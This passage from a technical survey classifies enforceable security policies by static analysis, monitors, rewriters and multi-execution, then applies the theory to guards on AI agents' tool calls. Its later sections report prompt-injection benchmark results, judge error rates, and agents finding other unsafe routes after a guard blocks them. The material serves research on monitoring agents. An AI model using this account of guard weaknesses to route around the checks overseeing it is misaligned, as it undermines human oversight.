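Devriese and Piessens solve this problem by running the program several times, once for each security level. With two levels, there is a public copy and a secret copy, and the mechanism follows these rules:

- Each copy produces only the outputs at its own level. The mechanism skips all the others.
- The public copy gets a default value in place of each secret input. The secret copy gets the real values of all inputs.
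- When both copies need the same public input, the public copy reads it first and the secret copy reuses the result.

The last rule matters because reading an input can have side effects. For example, if the program prompts the user with "Are you sure?", the user should have to answer only once.

In the email example, the two copies do the following:

| Operation | Public copy | Secret copy |
|---|---|---|
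| Read the email's text | gets a default value | gets the real text |
| Build the image's address | uses the default value | uses the real text |
| Request the image | sends the request | skips the request |

The image still loads, but the request no longer contains anything from the email. If the program also sends the email through a secret channel, the secret copy of the program sends the real text there.

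Every program becomes noninterfering under this mechanism, because the only copy that can produce public outputs never receives a secret. Devriese and Piessens prove this even for attackers who observe timing and termination, provided the public copy always runs first. The public copy then never waits for the secret copy, so its speed can't depend on a secret.

The mechanism also preserves the behavior of programs that were already noninterfering. In such a program, replacing the secrets with default values doesn't change the public outputs, so the public copy produces the same public outputs as the original program. The secret copy gets all the real inputs, so it produces the same secret outputs. The proof compares the outputs on each channel separately, so the relative order of outputs on different channels may change. It also covers only runs that terminate, and requires that secrets don't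 affect whether the program terminates.

Some harmless programs that never terminate do change. Suppose a program produces one secret output and then loops forever. If the secret copy must wait for the public copy to finish, it never runs, and the output never appears. Devriese and Piessens suggest a more flexible schedule but leave open whether it would still protect against timing attacks. *Impossibility of Precise and Sound Termination-Sensitive Security Enforcements* (Ngo, Piessens and Rezk, 2018) addresses the more general limit on enforcement.

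Programs that violated the policy keep running but may behave oddly. Suppose a program reads a secret and then reads a public input only if the secret differs from the default value. The public copy of the program gets the default value instead of the secret, so it never reads the public input. If the real secret differs from the default, the secret copy waits forever for the public copy to read that input. RW2 allows this behavior, though it could confuse the user.

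### What the extra copies cost

Devriese and Piessens tested the method with two security levels on SpiderMonkey, Mozilla's JavaScript engine, running standard benchmarks on a dual-core computer. Running the copies one after the other took about twice as long or longer on most benchmarks but needed little extra memory. Running them in parallel took 2% to 25% longer but used 50% to 100% more memory.

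One extra benchmark, which spent much of its time waiting for inputs and outputs, ran faster as two parallel copies than as the original program. The copies could wait at the same time instead of waiting for each operation in turn, as the original did. Every operation included an artificial delay of 10 milliseconds, so real programs would probably gain less.

The computation required grows quickly with the number of levels. If a system has to track whose data influenced each output, every possible set of people is a level, so ten people give 1,024 levels and twenty give more than a million. Algehed and Flanagan prove that any secure and transparent mechanism that doesn't look at the program's code takes time exponential in the number of people.

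Mechanisms that look at the code can avoid some of the repeated work, but Algehed and Flanagan also prove that every secure and transparent mechanism is equivalent to some form of multi-execution, up to a polynomial difference in running time. This suggests that poor engineering is not the only reason for the high overhead. It also helps to explain why *Multi-Execution Lattices Fast and Slow* (Algehed and Flanagan, 2021) still found that most automatic methods without false alarms were based on multi-execution.

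### Enforcing policies on black-box programs

Multi-execution can enforce many policies besides noninterference. In *Runtime Enforcement of Security Policies on Black Box Reactive Programs*, Ngo, Massacci and colleagues (2015) ask which policies a mechanism can enforce if it can run extra copies of a program and change their inputs and outputs, but can't look at the code. They consider programs that answer every input with an output in finite time. The mechanism must do the same, so it can't hold events back the way an edit automaton does.

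They prove that such a mechanism can enforce only hypersafety policies, a class that Clarkson and Schneider had defined. A policy belongs to this class if every program that violates it has a finite set of finite runs that could not all belong to a compliant program. If *k* runs are always enough to show a violation, the policy is a *k*-safety policy.

"No message after reading a file" is a 1-safety policy, because one bad run shows the violation. Noninterference is a 2-safety policy in this model, because a violation consists of two runs with the same public inputs and different public outputs. *k* can also be larger. If a secret consists of five shares and a program must not reveal all of them, even in separate runs, it may take five runs to show a violation.

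Some hypersafety policies cannot be enforced. One example is the policy that a program may output only the texts of programs that halt. A single bad output violates this policy, but a mechanism would have to solve the halting problem to decide whether to allow each output. Ngo and colleagues therefore define testable policies, for which an algorithm can decide whether any finite set of runs is compatible with the policy. They prove that black-box mechanisms can enforce every testable hypersafety policy that at least one program satisfies.

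#### Choosing which other runs to check

One enforcement mechanism runs the program on the actual input and on a finite number of alternative inputs. If the results together violate the policy, it replaces the latest output with an acceptable one.

Infinitely many other inputs could reveal a violation of noninterference, but the mechanism only needs to compare the public output for the actual input with the public output for the same input with all secrets removed. Suppose two inputs have the same public part but lead to different public outputs. Removing the secrets from either one gives the same input, whose public output can match at most one of the two original outputs. The mechanism therefore detects the violation on at least one of the original inputs. With this comparison, the mechanism closely resembles secure multi-execution.

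Corrections to different runs must also be compatible. Ngo and colleagues illustrate this with a policy for programs that read and write bits, which requires that flipping every input bit flips every output bit. Suppose a program always outputs 0. On input 0, a simple mechanism detects that the program would also output 0 on input 1, so it changes the output to 1. On input 1, it detects the same violation and again changes the output to 1. The corrected program always outputs 1, which still violates the policy.

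The mechanism solves this by correcting the runs in a fixed order. When the latest input bit is 0, it leaves the output unchanged. When the latest bit is 1, it compares the current output with the already corrected output for the opposite input, and flips the current output if necessary. The program in the example then outputs 0 for 0 and 1 for 1, as the policy requires.

The general construction is very slow because it may check a huge number of alternatives. An efficient mechanism needs a small set of alternatives that is still sufficient. Noninterference has such a set, but Ngo and colleagues couldn't find one for the policy about shares of a secret.

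#### Why these comparisons always finish

These results don't contradict the proof that a monitor can't enforce the secret-file policy by simulating two runs. Every program in the 2015 model must respond to each input in finite time, so the mechanism can compare the runs one output at a time and never has to wait forever. This requirement excludes the program *M* from the earlier proof, because *M* may run *N* forever without responding.

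In a doctoral thesis, Ngo finds that if programs can get stuck, the enforceable policies have to meet a condition on termination instead. More recently, Hsu, Oliveira da Costa and colleagues (2025) compared black-box enforcement of hyperproperties with gray-box and white-box enforcement in *Gray-box runtime enforcement of hyperproperties*.

### Are these mechanisms monitors or rewriters?

Secure multi-execution looks like monitoring in practice. Devriese and Piessens run several copies of the program without changing its code, intercept the inputs and outputs, and use a scheduler to decide which copy runs next.

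However, it isn't an execution monitor in Schneider's sense, because it uses more than one execution. It also doesn't need to find a violation before it intervenes. It always gives the public copy default values, even if the program wouldn't have leaked anything, just as the secret-file rewriter always filters the listing.

These mechanisms therefore count as rewriters in the classification. Ngo and colleagues, like Algehed and Flanagan, define an enforcement mechanism as a function that turns any program into another program, under conditions that are essentially RW1 and RW2. A rewriter could produce such a program by combining the copies, the scheduler and the rules for inputs and outputs.

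The secret-file rewriter is a special case that needs only one copy of the program. All of the program's outputs are public, so a secret copy would produce no output.

Ngo and colleagues point out that every policy enforceable by a black-box mechanism is also enforceable by rewriting. They couldn't find a policy that only a rewriter could enforce, even though a rewriter can also use the program's code. Their comparison covers policies about inputs and outputs, for programs that always respond, so it excludes policies about the program's text, such as "the program has fewer than one million states".

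### A policy no rewriter can enforce

Rewriting has limits too. Hamlen and colleagues prove that no rewriter can enforce the policy "the program halts on at least one input" if programs count as equivalent when they halt on the same inputs.

The proof shows that no rewriter can enforce this policy, because such a rewriter could be used to decide which programs satisfy it, and that is undecidable. For example, making every program halt on the input 0 satisfies RW1 but fails RW2, because it changes a compliant program that halts on 5 and runs forever on 0.

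Suppose such a rewriter *R* exists. To find out whether a program *M* halts on at least one input, we could do the following:

1. Build a program *M′* whose input consists of a number *i* and a string *s*. *M′* runs *M* on *s* for *i* steps. It halts if *M* halts within that time, and otherwise loops forever.
2. Compute *R*(*M′*). By RW1, this program halts on at least one input.
3. Search for such an input by running *R*(*M′*) on more and more inputs for more and more steps. The search must succeed eventually. Call the number it finds *j* and the string *t*.
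4. Run *M* on *t* for *j* steps.

If *M* halts in step 4, it halts on at least one input and we have the answer. If it doesn't, then *M′* loops forever on the input made up of *j* and *t*, although *R*(*M′*) halts on it. The two programs are therefore not equivalent, so by RW2, *M′* must violate the policy. This means *M′* never halts, so *M* doesn't halt on any input either.

We need the number *i* to make the last step finite. If we applied *R* directly to *M*, we could find an input on which *R*(*M*) halts, but determining whether *M* does too would be the halting problem again. With *M′*, the input also specifies how many steps to check.

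The same proof works for any stricter equivalence, such as one that also requires the same outputs, but only if equivalent programs still halt on the same inputs.

The opposite policy, "the program never halts on any input", is easy to enforce under the equivalence used in the proof. The rewriter can always return a program that loops forever, which is equivalent to every compliant program. No single program is equivalent to every program that halts on at least one input, because those programs may halt on different inputs.

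### No match with the arithmetic hierarchy

Static analysis can enforce exactly the decidable policies, and the four conditions on monitors describe exactly the coRE policies. Both classes are levels of the arithmetic hierarchy, but Hamlen and colleagues prove that the class of policies rewriters can enforce doesn't match any level.

The proof uses two of the policies above. A rewriter can enforce the universal-machine policy, which is Π₂-complete. Any level that contains this policy must contain all Π₂ policies, and therefore every RE policy, including "halts on at least one input". No rewriter can enforce this last policy, so no level contains exactly the policies that rewriters can enforce.

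The hierarchy ranks policies by how hard it is to decide whether a program complies. A rewriter doesn't have to decide this, so a policy's level is a poor guide to whether rewriting can enforce it. Rewriting can enforce a policy when some algorithm can make every program comply without changing the behavior of those that already do. Whether such an algorithm exists depends on both the policy and the definition of equivalent behavior.

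Hamlen's slides still list the exact class of policies enforceable by rewriting as an open question. In practice, most tools that insert checks into programs let users specify only what a single run may do, so users cannot express the secret-file policy. Hamlen and colleagues therefore called for usable languages for specifying policies that a monitor cannot enforce.

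## Which policies a monitor can keep from being violated

Conditions EM1 to EM4 give only an upper bound on the policies that execution monitors can enforce. Under these conditions, the enforceable policies are the class coRE. Hamlen and colleagues found coRE policies that no rewriter can enforce, even though a rewriter can build a monitor into the program that the monitor controls. After looking at these policies more closely, they concluded that no real monitor can enforce them either.

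The conditions describe only the untrusted program's own executions, not what happens once the monitor intervenes. Intervention can fail because every available response would itself violate the policy, or because the monitor detects the violation too late.

### When every available response is forbidden

Schneider's monitor can only terminate the program, so it can't enforce the policy "the program never halts on any input". This policy is coRE, because a detector that scans the execution for an "ended" event meets all four conditions. But when a program is about to halt, the monitor can only halt it. It also can't enforce "the program writes a log entry before it ends", because terminating a program that has not yet written one violates the policy.

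Hamlen and colleagues represent a monitor's response as the sequence of events that replaces the rest of the execution. A monitor cannot enforce a policy that forbids all of its responses. If it could replace the rest of the execution with any sequence of events, the only such policy would be the one that no program satisfies.

Sometimes the monitor can't stop the event that causes the violation. Basin and colleagues distinguish events that a monitor can prevent from events that it can only observe, such as failures and clock ticks. They compare two rules:

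- After a failure, nobody may log in for three time units.
- Every request must lead to a delivery within three time units, unless the system stops first.

The login rule and the delivery rule are both safety properties. A monitor can enforce the login rule by blocking logins until enough ticks have passed. It can't enforce the delivery rule, because a tick completes the violation and the monitor can't prevent ticks. In this model, a monitor stops the system only when it intercepts an event it can prevent, so it can't step in just before the deadline. Blocking the request would also be wrong, because the delivery might have come on time.

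Basin and colleagues prove that a monitor can enforce a rule about executions exactly when the rule allows the empty execution, every violation becomes irreparable at an event the monitor can prevent, and an algorithm can decide whether any finite sequence of events is the beginning of an allowed execution. If a finite automaton describes the rule, an algorithm can check whether a monitor can enforce it, although the check may take a very long time. If the automaton has a stack, no algorithm can check this for every such rule.

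A monitor avoids the problem if its response to a forbidden action cannot itself violate the policy. *What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) analyzes a gate that reviews each action of an AI agent before the action takes effect. The gate can replace a forbidden action with one that has no external effect, and the agent then continues. In this model, blocking an action never causes a violation. If the gate judges each action correctly, it can enforce every satisfiable safety policy for which an algorithm can decide whether the actions so far already violate it.

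### Recognizing a violation too late

Hamlen and colleagues illustrate late recognition with a trusted service that lends a resource to untrusted programs. Once a program has the resource, the service cannot take it back or halt the program. But the program can declare that it has finished with the resource, and the service may then lend it to another program. The policy requires that a program never use the resource again after making this declaration.

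Two detectors express this policy:

- The look-ahead detector fails an execution at a release if the program could still use the resource afterwards, on any further input.
- The look-back detector fails an execution at a use if a release came earlier.

(The original formula for the look-ahead detector passes an execution again once the last use is over, which breaks EM2. In the version here, an execution that has failed stays failed.)

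Both detectors induce the same policy. If a program can use the resource after releasing it, some execution contains a release followed by a use. The look-ahead detector rejects that execution at the release, and the look-back detector rejects it at the use. If a program can never do this, both detectors accept all its executions.

The difference is in the timing. Suppose program A uses the resource, releases it, computes something and then uses it again:

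| Event | Who may use the resource | Look-ahead detector | Look-back detector |
|---|---|---|---|
| A uses the resource | A | passes | passes |
| A releases the resource | nobody, until the service lends it again | fails | passes |
| A computes while the service lends the resource to B | B | already failed | passes |
| A uses the resource | B, but A uses it too | already failed | fails |

A monitor based on the look-ahead detector would suppress the release, and the service would never lend the resource to B. A monitor based on the look-back detector would detect nothing until A tried to use the resource again. By then B would have it, and the service couldn't stop either program.

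No algorithm can compute the look-ahead detector. A program could release the resource, run another program *N* on an input *x*, and use the resource if *N* halts. To assess the release, the monitor would have to determine whether *N* halts on *x*.

An edit automaton could hold back the release, but it could never determine when to let it through, because no event shows that the program has stopped needing the resource.

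The four conditions do not rule out this problem because they require only that *some* suitable detector exists, and the look-back detector qualifies. Viswanathan had shown that the Java monitor MaC could enforce all coRE policies. Hamlen and colleagues call proofs of this kind misleading because MaC can report the early release only after it has happened.

### Making the monitor part of the program

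The conditions on rewriters are stricter because RW1 applies to the finished program, including any monitor inside it. Hamlen and colleagues use this to write a monitor's limits into the policy. They add an event that appears on the trace whenever a monitor suppresses a use of the resource, and forbid that event. A rewriter must then produce programs that never use the resource after a release and never have a use suppressed.

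No rewriter can do this if equivalent programs must release the resource on the same inputs, and if halting or replacing the program to avoid a use also counts as suppression. Suppose a program releases the resource, runs *N* on *x*, and then uses the resource if *N* halts. If *N* runs forever, the program complies, so by RW2 its rewritten version must release the resource. If *N* halts, the use has to go ahead, so the rewritten version must never release the resource. We could therefore solve the halting problem by running *N* and the rewritten program side by side until either *N* halts or the rewritten program releases the resource.

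The extended policy is still coRE, because a search through all executions would find any suppressed use or use after a release. So it belongs to the class that monitors were supposed to be able to enforce, although no rewriter can enforce it.

### Benevolent detectors

To describe detectors that a monitor can act on in time, Hamlen and colleagues define benevolence. A detector *D* is benevolent if there is an algorithm *A* that accepts or rejects every finite prefix in finite time and meets two conditions for every program *M*:

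- B1: If some execution of *M* fails *D*, then *A* rejects every prefix of *M*'s executions that fails *D*.
- B2: If every execution of *M* passes *D*, then *A* accepts every prefix of *M*'s executions.

Before each event takes effect, the monitor applies *A* to the events so far plus that event. B1 ensures that the monitor catches every failure in a program that violates the policy, though it may also intervene early in such a program or reject some of the program's harmless prefixes. B2 ensures that the monitor never interferes with a compliant program.

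The look-back detector is benevolent because *A* only has to scan the prefix for a use after a release. The look-ahead detector is not benevolent because, in the program that runs *N* after releasing the resource, *A* would have to reject the release if *N* halts and accept it if *N* runs forever.

Every coRE policy has a detector that meets EM2 and EM4, and any such detector is benevolent because *A* can apply the detector itself. However, the detector may fail an execution long after the damage is done. Benevolence guarantees that a monitor can act before the detector fails the execution, so it is useful only if the detector fails it early enough. It is therefore more informative to ask whether every reasonable detector for a policy is benevolent.

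### The intersection theorem

Hamlen and colleagues prove that this is true of policies that are both coRE and enforceable by rewriting, for equivalences suited to inlined monitors. Such an equivalence has two properties:

- EQ1: An algorithm can decide whether two finite executions are equivalent.
- EQ2: If two executions are equivalent, then every prefix of one is equivalent to some prefix of the other.

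The two prefixes in EQ2 can have different lengths. An inlined monitor adds steps for its checks, and after each successful check the program returns to a point that matches the original.

The theorem applies to a detector *D* that meets EM2 and is consistent with the equivalence, meaning that it gives equivalent executions the same verdict. If the policy *D* induces is coRE and some rewriter *R* enforces it, then *D* is benevolent.

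The proof constructs *A* from two algorithms that must exist: the rewriter *R*, and a search *V* that halts on a program exactly when the program violates the policy. Given a prefix *χ*, *A* works as follows:

1. It reads the text of *M* from the first event, computes *R*(*M*), and collects the input symbols that *M* has read so far.
2. It runs *R*(*M*) on those symbols for one event. If the result is equivalent to *χ*, it accepts.
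3. Otherwise, it runs *V* on *M* for one step. If *V* halts, it rejects.
4. If neither happens, it repeats steps 2 and 3 with two events and two steps, then three, and so on.

Suppose *M* satisfies the policy. Then *V* never halts, so *A* cannot reject. By RW2, *M* and *R*(*M*) have equivalent executions on the same input, and by EQ2 some prefix of *R*(*M*)'s execution is equivalent to *χ*. *A* eventually finds that prefix and accepts, which proves B2.

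Now suppose *M* violates the policy. *V* eventually halts, so *A* always accepts or rejects. If *A* accepts *χ*, then *χ* is equivalent to a prefix of an execution of *R*(*M*). That execution passes *D* by RW1, its prefix passes by EM2, and *χ* passes by consistency. *A* therefore never accepts a prefix that fails *D*, so it rejects every such prefix, which proves B1.

*A* in effect compares *M* with the rewritten program, which obeys the policy. With the boot-sector policy, for example, *R*(*M*) halts before any forbidden write. If *M* is about to make such a write, *A* finds no match for it in *R*(*M*)'s execution and keeps looking until *V* confirms that *M* violates the policy.

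### What is proved and what is only argued

Hamlen and colleagues write in their introduction that monitors can enforce exactly the policies that are both coRE and rewritable. They are rightly more cautious in their summary, where they claim only to have argued that this intersection is a more accurate description of the policies monitors can enforce.

The theorem shows when a monitor can detect a violation, but not whether the monitor can respond suitably. A rewriter may replace a program that violates the policy with any program that complies, while a particular monitor may only be able to terminate it. So a policy can be in the intersection even though Schneider's monitor can't enforce it.

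The argument in the other direction is informal. If a monitor can enforce a policy, a rewriter should be able to insert that monitor into every program, and the result should meet RW1 and RW2. This is plausible as long as the equivalence ignores the inserted code. But the 2006 model does not independently define what a real monitor can do, so a proof would have nothing to compare the intersection with.

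In the resource example, the look-ahead detector is not benevolent. By the theorem, if an equivalence has both EQ properties and the detector is consistent with it, no rewriter can enforce the policy under that equivalence. If the equivalence instead ignores the program's text and any extra steps for checks, the detector is inconsistent with it. Two programs might both release the resource, read a 0 and do nothing more, although one of them would have used the resource after reading a 1. Their executions are equivalent, but the detector rejects only that one. Under this equivalence, a rewriter can enforce the policy by stopping the program just before it uses the released resource, if the setting allows that.

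### The "never halts" counterexample

Hamlen and colleagues also prove that some coRE policies have detectors that are not benevolent. Their example is the policy "the program never halts on any input", and their detector accepts an execution exactly when the program named in its first event never halts. They use identity as the equivalence relation, so two executions are equivalent only if all their events are the same.

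This detector depends only on the program's text, so it meets EM2 and EM3. Like every detector, it is consistent with identity. But it is not benevolent, because if it were, *A* could read the first event of any program and decide whether that program ever halts, which is impossible. By the intersection theorem, no rewriter can enforce the policy under identity.

The proof is correct, but it shows little about halting. The first event encodes the program's text, so when equivalence is identity, any edit makes a program inequivalent to the original, and rewriting can enforce no more than static analysis can. Rewriting therefore can't enforce the boot-sector policy either, though that policy is the standard example of what monitors can enforce. The same proof works for it, with a detector that passes an execution exactly when the program encoded in its first event never writes to the boot sector.

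The result changes if the equivalence ignores the first event and compares all the others. Identity apart from the text still has both EQ properties. The detector is no longer consistent with it, because a program that never halts can produce the same later events as one that would halt on a different input. And a rewriter can now enforce the policy by replacing every instruction to halt with an endless loop that does nothing:

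- RW1 holds because the new program has no way to halt.
- RW2 holds because a compliant program never reaches the replaced instructions, so it produces the same events as before, apart from its text.

Under this equivalence, "never halts" is both coRE and rewritable. A monitor can enforce this policy by making a program idle, but not if its only possible response is to terminate the program.

### Handing over a harmful program

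There are better examples of coRE policies that rewriters can't enforce. *No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) studies filters and monitors for language models. In one of its cases, a program delivers strings to a machine that may run them. Suppose the policy forbids delivering any program that would perform a harmful action when run on a fixed input.

This policy is coRE because an algorithm can run the untrusted program on more and more inputs, run every program it delivers, and halt if one does harm. A detector can also meet all four conditions by running each delivered program for as many steps as the execution has events so far, and failing the execution if harm has occurred. Each check is finite, but the detector may fail the execution a million events after the delivery.

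No rewriter can enforce the policy under any equivalence that preserves what a program delivers. For any program *p*, consider the program that delivers *p* and then idles. The rewritten version must still deliver *p* if *p* is harmless, but must not if *p* is harmful. We could therefore decide whether *p* is harmful by running *p* and the rewritten program side by side until either *p* did harm or the rewritten program delivered *p*. This would solve the halting problem, because *p* might run a program *N* on an input *x* and do harm only if *N* halts.

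Amer and colleagues prove directly that no monitor can do it either. They consider a monitor that can stop a program before any action, and call it exact if it prevents every forbidden sequence of actions and never stops a permitted one. An exact monitor exists if and only if an algorithm can decide which finite sequences are forbidden, because running an exact monitor on a sequence shows whether that sequence is permitted. In the delivery example, deciding whether a sequence is forbidden means deciding whether a delivered program is harmful.

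This condition resembles EM4 but is stronger, because EM4 allows a detector to delay its verdict. Amer and colleagues, Basin and colleagues, and Ray all require a decision about whether the events so far *already* amount to a violation. This seems to be the right requirement for any monitor meant to prevent harm.

The practical solution is often to check a later event. If a monitor also controls the machine that runs the delivered program, it can allow the delivery and block the harmful action when the program attempts it. The monitor needs only a list of forbidden actions and the ability to observe and stop each one.

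### Where each policy falls

Pérez-Acle (2026), in *No finite rulebook can certify every safe program*, confirms several of these placements with a different approach, asking which verdicts about a program can be established by finite evidence. Finite evidence can establish every violation of "never perform a forbidden action" but not every case of compliance, so the policy is coRE and undecidable.

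One rule might require a program to publish the same report whichever of two secrets it receives. In general, evidence can establish neither that a program obeys this rule nor that it violates it. The same is true of the secret-file policy when judged by outputs alone, and of the rule that every request must eventually get an answer.

A rewriter can't enforce the rule about requests either, if compliant programs must keep their answers. If one could, we could number all programs and rewrite each of them so that it answers every request. We could then write a program that answers request *n* by adding 1 to the *n*th rewritten program's answer to request *n*. This program always answers, so its own rewritten version must give the same answers. But if it is program number *k*, its answer to request *k* is 1 more than its rewritten version's, which is a contradiction. If the rewriter were allowed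 to change the content of compliant programs' answers, it could enforce the rule by replacing every program with one that answers 0 to every request.

In the table, two programs are equivalent if they have the same events and outputs, ignoring their text and any extra idle steps. For the universal-machine policy and "halts on at least one input", programs are instead equivalent if they halt on the same inputs. The last column assumes that the monitor has the program's text.

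| Policy | Static analysis | coRE | Rewriting | Monitor |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Halts within 100 steps | yes | yes | yes | yes |
| The policy that no program satisfies | yes | yes | no | no |
| Never writes to the boot sector | no | yes | yes | yes |
| Sends no message after reading a file | no | yes | yes | yes |
| Never halts | no | yes | yes | only if it can make the program idle |
| Writes a log entry before it ends | no | yes | yes | only if it can add the entry or make the program idle |
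| Never uses a resource after releasing it, if the monitor can block the use | no | yes | yes | yes |
| The same, if nothing can block the use | no | yes | no | no |
| Never delivers a harmful program | no | yes | no | no |
| Secret file, judged by outputs alone | no | no | yes | no |
| Halts on the same inputs as the universal machine | no | no | yes | no |
| Halts on at least one input | no | no | no | no |
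| Answers every request eventually | no | no | no | no |

Hamlen and colleagues' diagram places policies that forbid every response a monitor can make outside the rewritable class. The rows for "never halts" and the log entry differ from the diagram because a rewriter can make changes that a monitor that works by terminating the program cannot.

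## Guards on an AI agent's tool calls as execution monitors

An AI agent is a language model plus scaffolding, the ordinary code around it. The model only produces text. The scaffolding builds the model's input, recognizes when the output requests a tool, runs the tool and puts the result into the next input. An agent that arranges travel, for example, might search for flights, read the results and request a payment. A guard that checks each request before the scaffolding carries it out is an execution monitor.

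### An agent as a program

The parts of an agent correspond to the program machine of Hamlen and colleagues as follows:

| Program machine | Agent |
|---|---|
| program text | the model's weights and the scaffolding's code |
| input tape | user messages, tool results and the random numbers for sampling |
| work tape | the text the model is working on and any notes the agent keeps |
| events | tool calls |

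To produce text, the model computes a probability for every possible next token, which is a word or part of one. The software then picks a token at random according to these probabilities, a step called sampling. If the random numbers used in sampling count as input, the rest of the agent is deterministic, as the program machine has to be.

A policy covers every possible input, so an agent satisfies "never pay a stranger" only if no web page or email, even one written by an attacker, could lead it to pay one. Sampling makes this even harder, because models usually give every token at least a tiny probability, and almost any tool call can therefore occur unless the software discards unlikely tokens. Nearly every unguarded agent with a payment tool thus violates the policy. Conditions such as RW2 and B2 protect only compliant programs, so they barely restrict what a guard may do to such an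 agent. A more useful requirement for agents is that a guard leave compliant *executions* unchanged.

Guarding tool calls is easier in one respect than the task of the 2006 monitor, which has to predict the program's next step. The guard can check the model's written request before it takes effect, because nothing happens until the scaffolding acts on it.

### What access to the weights adds

The 2006 monitor also has the program's text. For an agent, part of this text is the scaffolding's code, which a guard can analyze like any other program. Most of it is the model's weights, the billions of numbers that training produces. They contain no readable rule such as "if the fare is under $500, request the payment", so a guard generally has to run the model to find out what it would do in a given situation. If the guard also has the random numbers used to sample the model's output, it can predict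 the next tool call exactly, but not what happens after that, because that depends on a tool result the guard doesn't have yet.

Many agents use a model available only over the internet, so their guards don't have its weights to run. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) describes a monitor that doesn't need them. The monitor treats the agent as an untrusted component that may attempt anything, records which messages, tool results and approvals influenced each proposed action, and checks this record against the policy. Such a guard is closer to Schneider's monitor than to the 2006 one.

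### Bounded context and external memory

A language model can read only a limited number of tokens at once, and the tokens it reads are called its context. *Computability of Agentic Systems* (Viriyasuthee, 2026) proves that a model with a finite context and no randomness is equivalent to a finite state machine, because there are only finitely many contexts and each one determines the next token. Checking every context would therefore show whether the model can ever request a particular tool. This is possible only in principle, because a model with 100,000 different tokens and a context of 100,000 tokens has 10^500,000 possible contexts.

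The argument fails if the agent has an external memory that can grow without limit. Viriyasuthee stores the tape of a Turing machine as a chain of notes, one for each cell. The model reads the current note and its neighbors, rewrites the current note and moves to the next one. Even a small context is then enough for any computation a Turing machine can do.

In *On the Turing Completeness of Transformers and Agents*, Qiao, Yu and colleagues (2026) find the same contrast between a single transformer, the type of neural network behind most language models, and an agent. A transformer with finite-precision numbers can't evaluate arithmetic expressions of every length, but an agent with a memory and simple tools can simulate any Turing machine. *SoK* (2025), a survey of trust and authorization in agents, concludes that predicting whether such an agent will take a particular sensitive action is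 equivalent to the halting problem.

Whether an agent's behavior is decidable depends on how its memory works. Viriyasuthee also shows that an agent that only splits tasks into nested subtasks and never rewrites earlier notes is no more powerful than a finite machine with a stack. Whether such a machine ever takes a given action is decidable. These proofs use models constructed for the purpose, and a trained model might make mistakes in such a long computation. But an agent that can write and run ordinary programs doesn't need to do the computation itself, so its behavior is undecidable in the same idealized sense as that of any other program. A guard avoids this problem because it only has to judge the call the agent requests.

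### Deciding before an irreversible action

The gate that Ray analyzes is a guard for actions that nobody can undo. The example is an assistant that sends email and transfers money under three rules:

- It must never email personal information to anyone who is not on an approved list.
- It must never transfer more than a fixed amount to one recipient in a day.
- It must send nothing after the user revokes its access.

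The gate tracks which actions have taken effect and can allow, block or replace the next one. Like an edit automaton, it must be sound and transparent, but here transparency means passing on every action of a compliant run unchanged and without delay.

Ray proves that a gate can do both exactly when the policy is a safety policy and the gate can recognize the policy's good prefixes, the sequences of actions that could still be extended into a compliant run. The gate then blocks any action that would produce a bad prefix.

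Conversely, if the policy is not a safety policy, some endless sequence of actions violates it even though every prefix could still continue into a compliant run. If the agent proposes these actions one by one, the gate has to allow each of them, because the agent might be on a compliant run, so it allows the whole forbidden sequence. Letting the gate make random decisions or replace actions doesn't help.

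No gate can enforce the policy "every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation". If the gate allows a payment, the confirmation may never come, and if it blocks the payment, it may interfere with an agent that would have confirmed. An edit automaton could hold the payment back until the agent confirms it, unless the agent needs the result of the payment first, but a gate has to decide immediately. A gate could instead require the agent to confirm each payment before making another. This is a safety policy, and it allows at most one payment that the agent never confirms.

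Ray presents the theorem as a refinement of the 2006 classification. It covers monitors that can't end the run and that face infinitely many possible actions, since amounts and addresses can vary without limit. The resulting class is smaller than coRE because the gate can't delay its decision on an action.

The gate's memory further limits which policies it can enforce. To enforce the daily limit, it needs a separate total for each recipient and day. Ray also considers whether one can check a set of rules before using it, for instance to find out whether it could ever block anything. This is undecidable if the rules can use two counters that they can raise, lower and test for zero. It is decidable for a more restricted language in which counters only go up and rules compare them only with fixed limits. That language can still express spending limits and revoked access.

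### When blocking changes what the agent does next

A simple program can check the daily limit, but the rule about personal information requires judging what an email contains. Guards often leave this to another language model, called a judge, which makes mistakes. Ray tested 23 judges on instructions from AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do office tasks while some of the data they read contains an attacker's instructions. When one of the better judges was required to miss at most 10% of violations, it blocked 78% of the legitimate instructions. When the limit was 5%, every judge had to block everything, because there were too few examples of violations to set a less strict threshold.

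Ray then ran a small agent on AgentDojo, with 949 episodes for each of three conditions. One condition had no gate, and the other two used judges with 7 billion and 3 billion parameters:

| Gate | Successful attacks | Tool calls blocked | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| none | 45 (4.7%) | 0% | 25.4% |
| 7-billion judge | 30 (3.2%) | 12% | 24.3% |
| 3-billion judge | 4 (0.4%) | 78% | 18.0% |

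The gate with the smaller judge prevented most attacks, but only by blocking most of what the agent tried to do. In the 560 office-workspace episodes, where no attack succeeded even without a gate, it blocked 85% of the calls, and the share of completed tasks fell from 26.4% to 16.3%. The other gate blocked much less, but its effect on attacks was not statistically significant across the benchmark. The two gates used different thresholds as well as different judges, so the results don't show that smaller judges are safer.

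In a second experiment, Ray compared the same 389 episodes with and without each gate. For the stricter gate, 34 attacks succeeded only when the gate was absent, and 5 succeeded only when it was present. For the more lenient gate, the numbers were 29 and 22. Ray concludes that blocking an action can lead the agent into an attack that would not otherwise have happened.

That is plausible, but the numbers are weak evidence for it. Without any gate, these 389 episodes produced 45 successful attacks in the first experiment and 38 in the second, so at least seven outcomes changed by chance. Chance could also explain the 5 attacks under the stricter gate and many of the 22 under the other.

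Ray also gives a theoretical argument that doesn't depend on these counts. Suppose two agents behave identically as long as nothing blocks them. After a block, one stops and the other attempts a different violation. No record made without a gate can distinguish them, so one has to test a gate by running agents with it. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), a survey, reports that agents in another benchmark found other unsafe ways to proceed after a guard blocked a direct violation.

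The theorem about gates still holds for agents that react to being blocked, because it covers every possible series of proposals. Repeated attempts can't get a violation past a gate that judges every action correctly, but if the gate is fallible, each new attempt is another chance for a mistake.

Blocking tool calls can also help an agent complete its task. *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) tested small, fixed checks in a benchmark whose tools don't reject forbidden calls. Some of these calls would have corrupted the data and made the task impossible, so blocking them raised the success rate.

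### When a disclosure depends on a private reason

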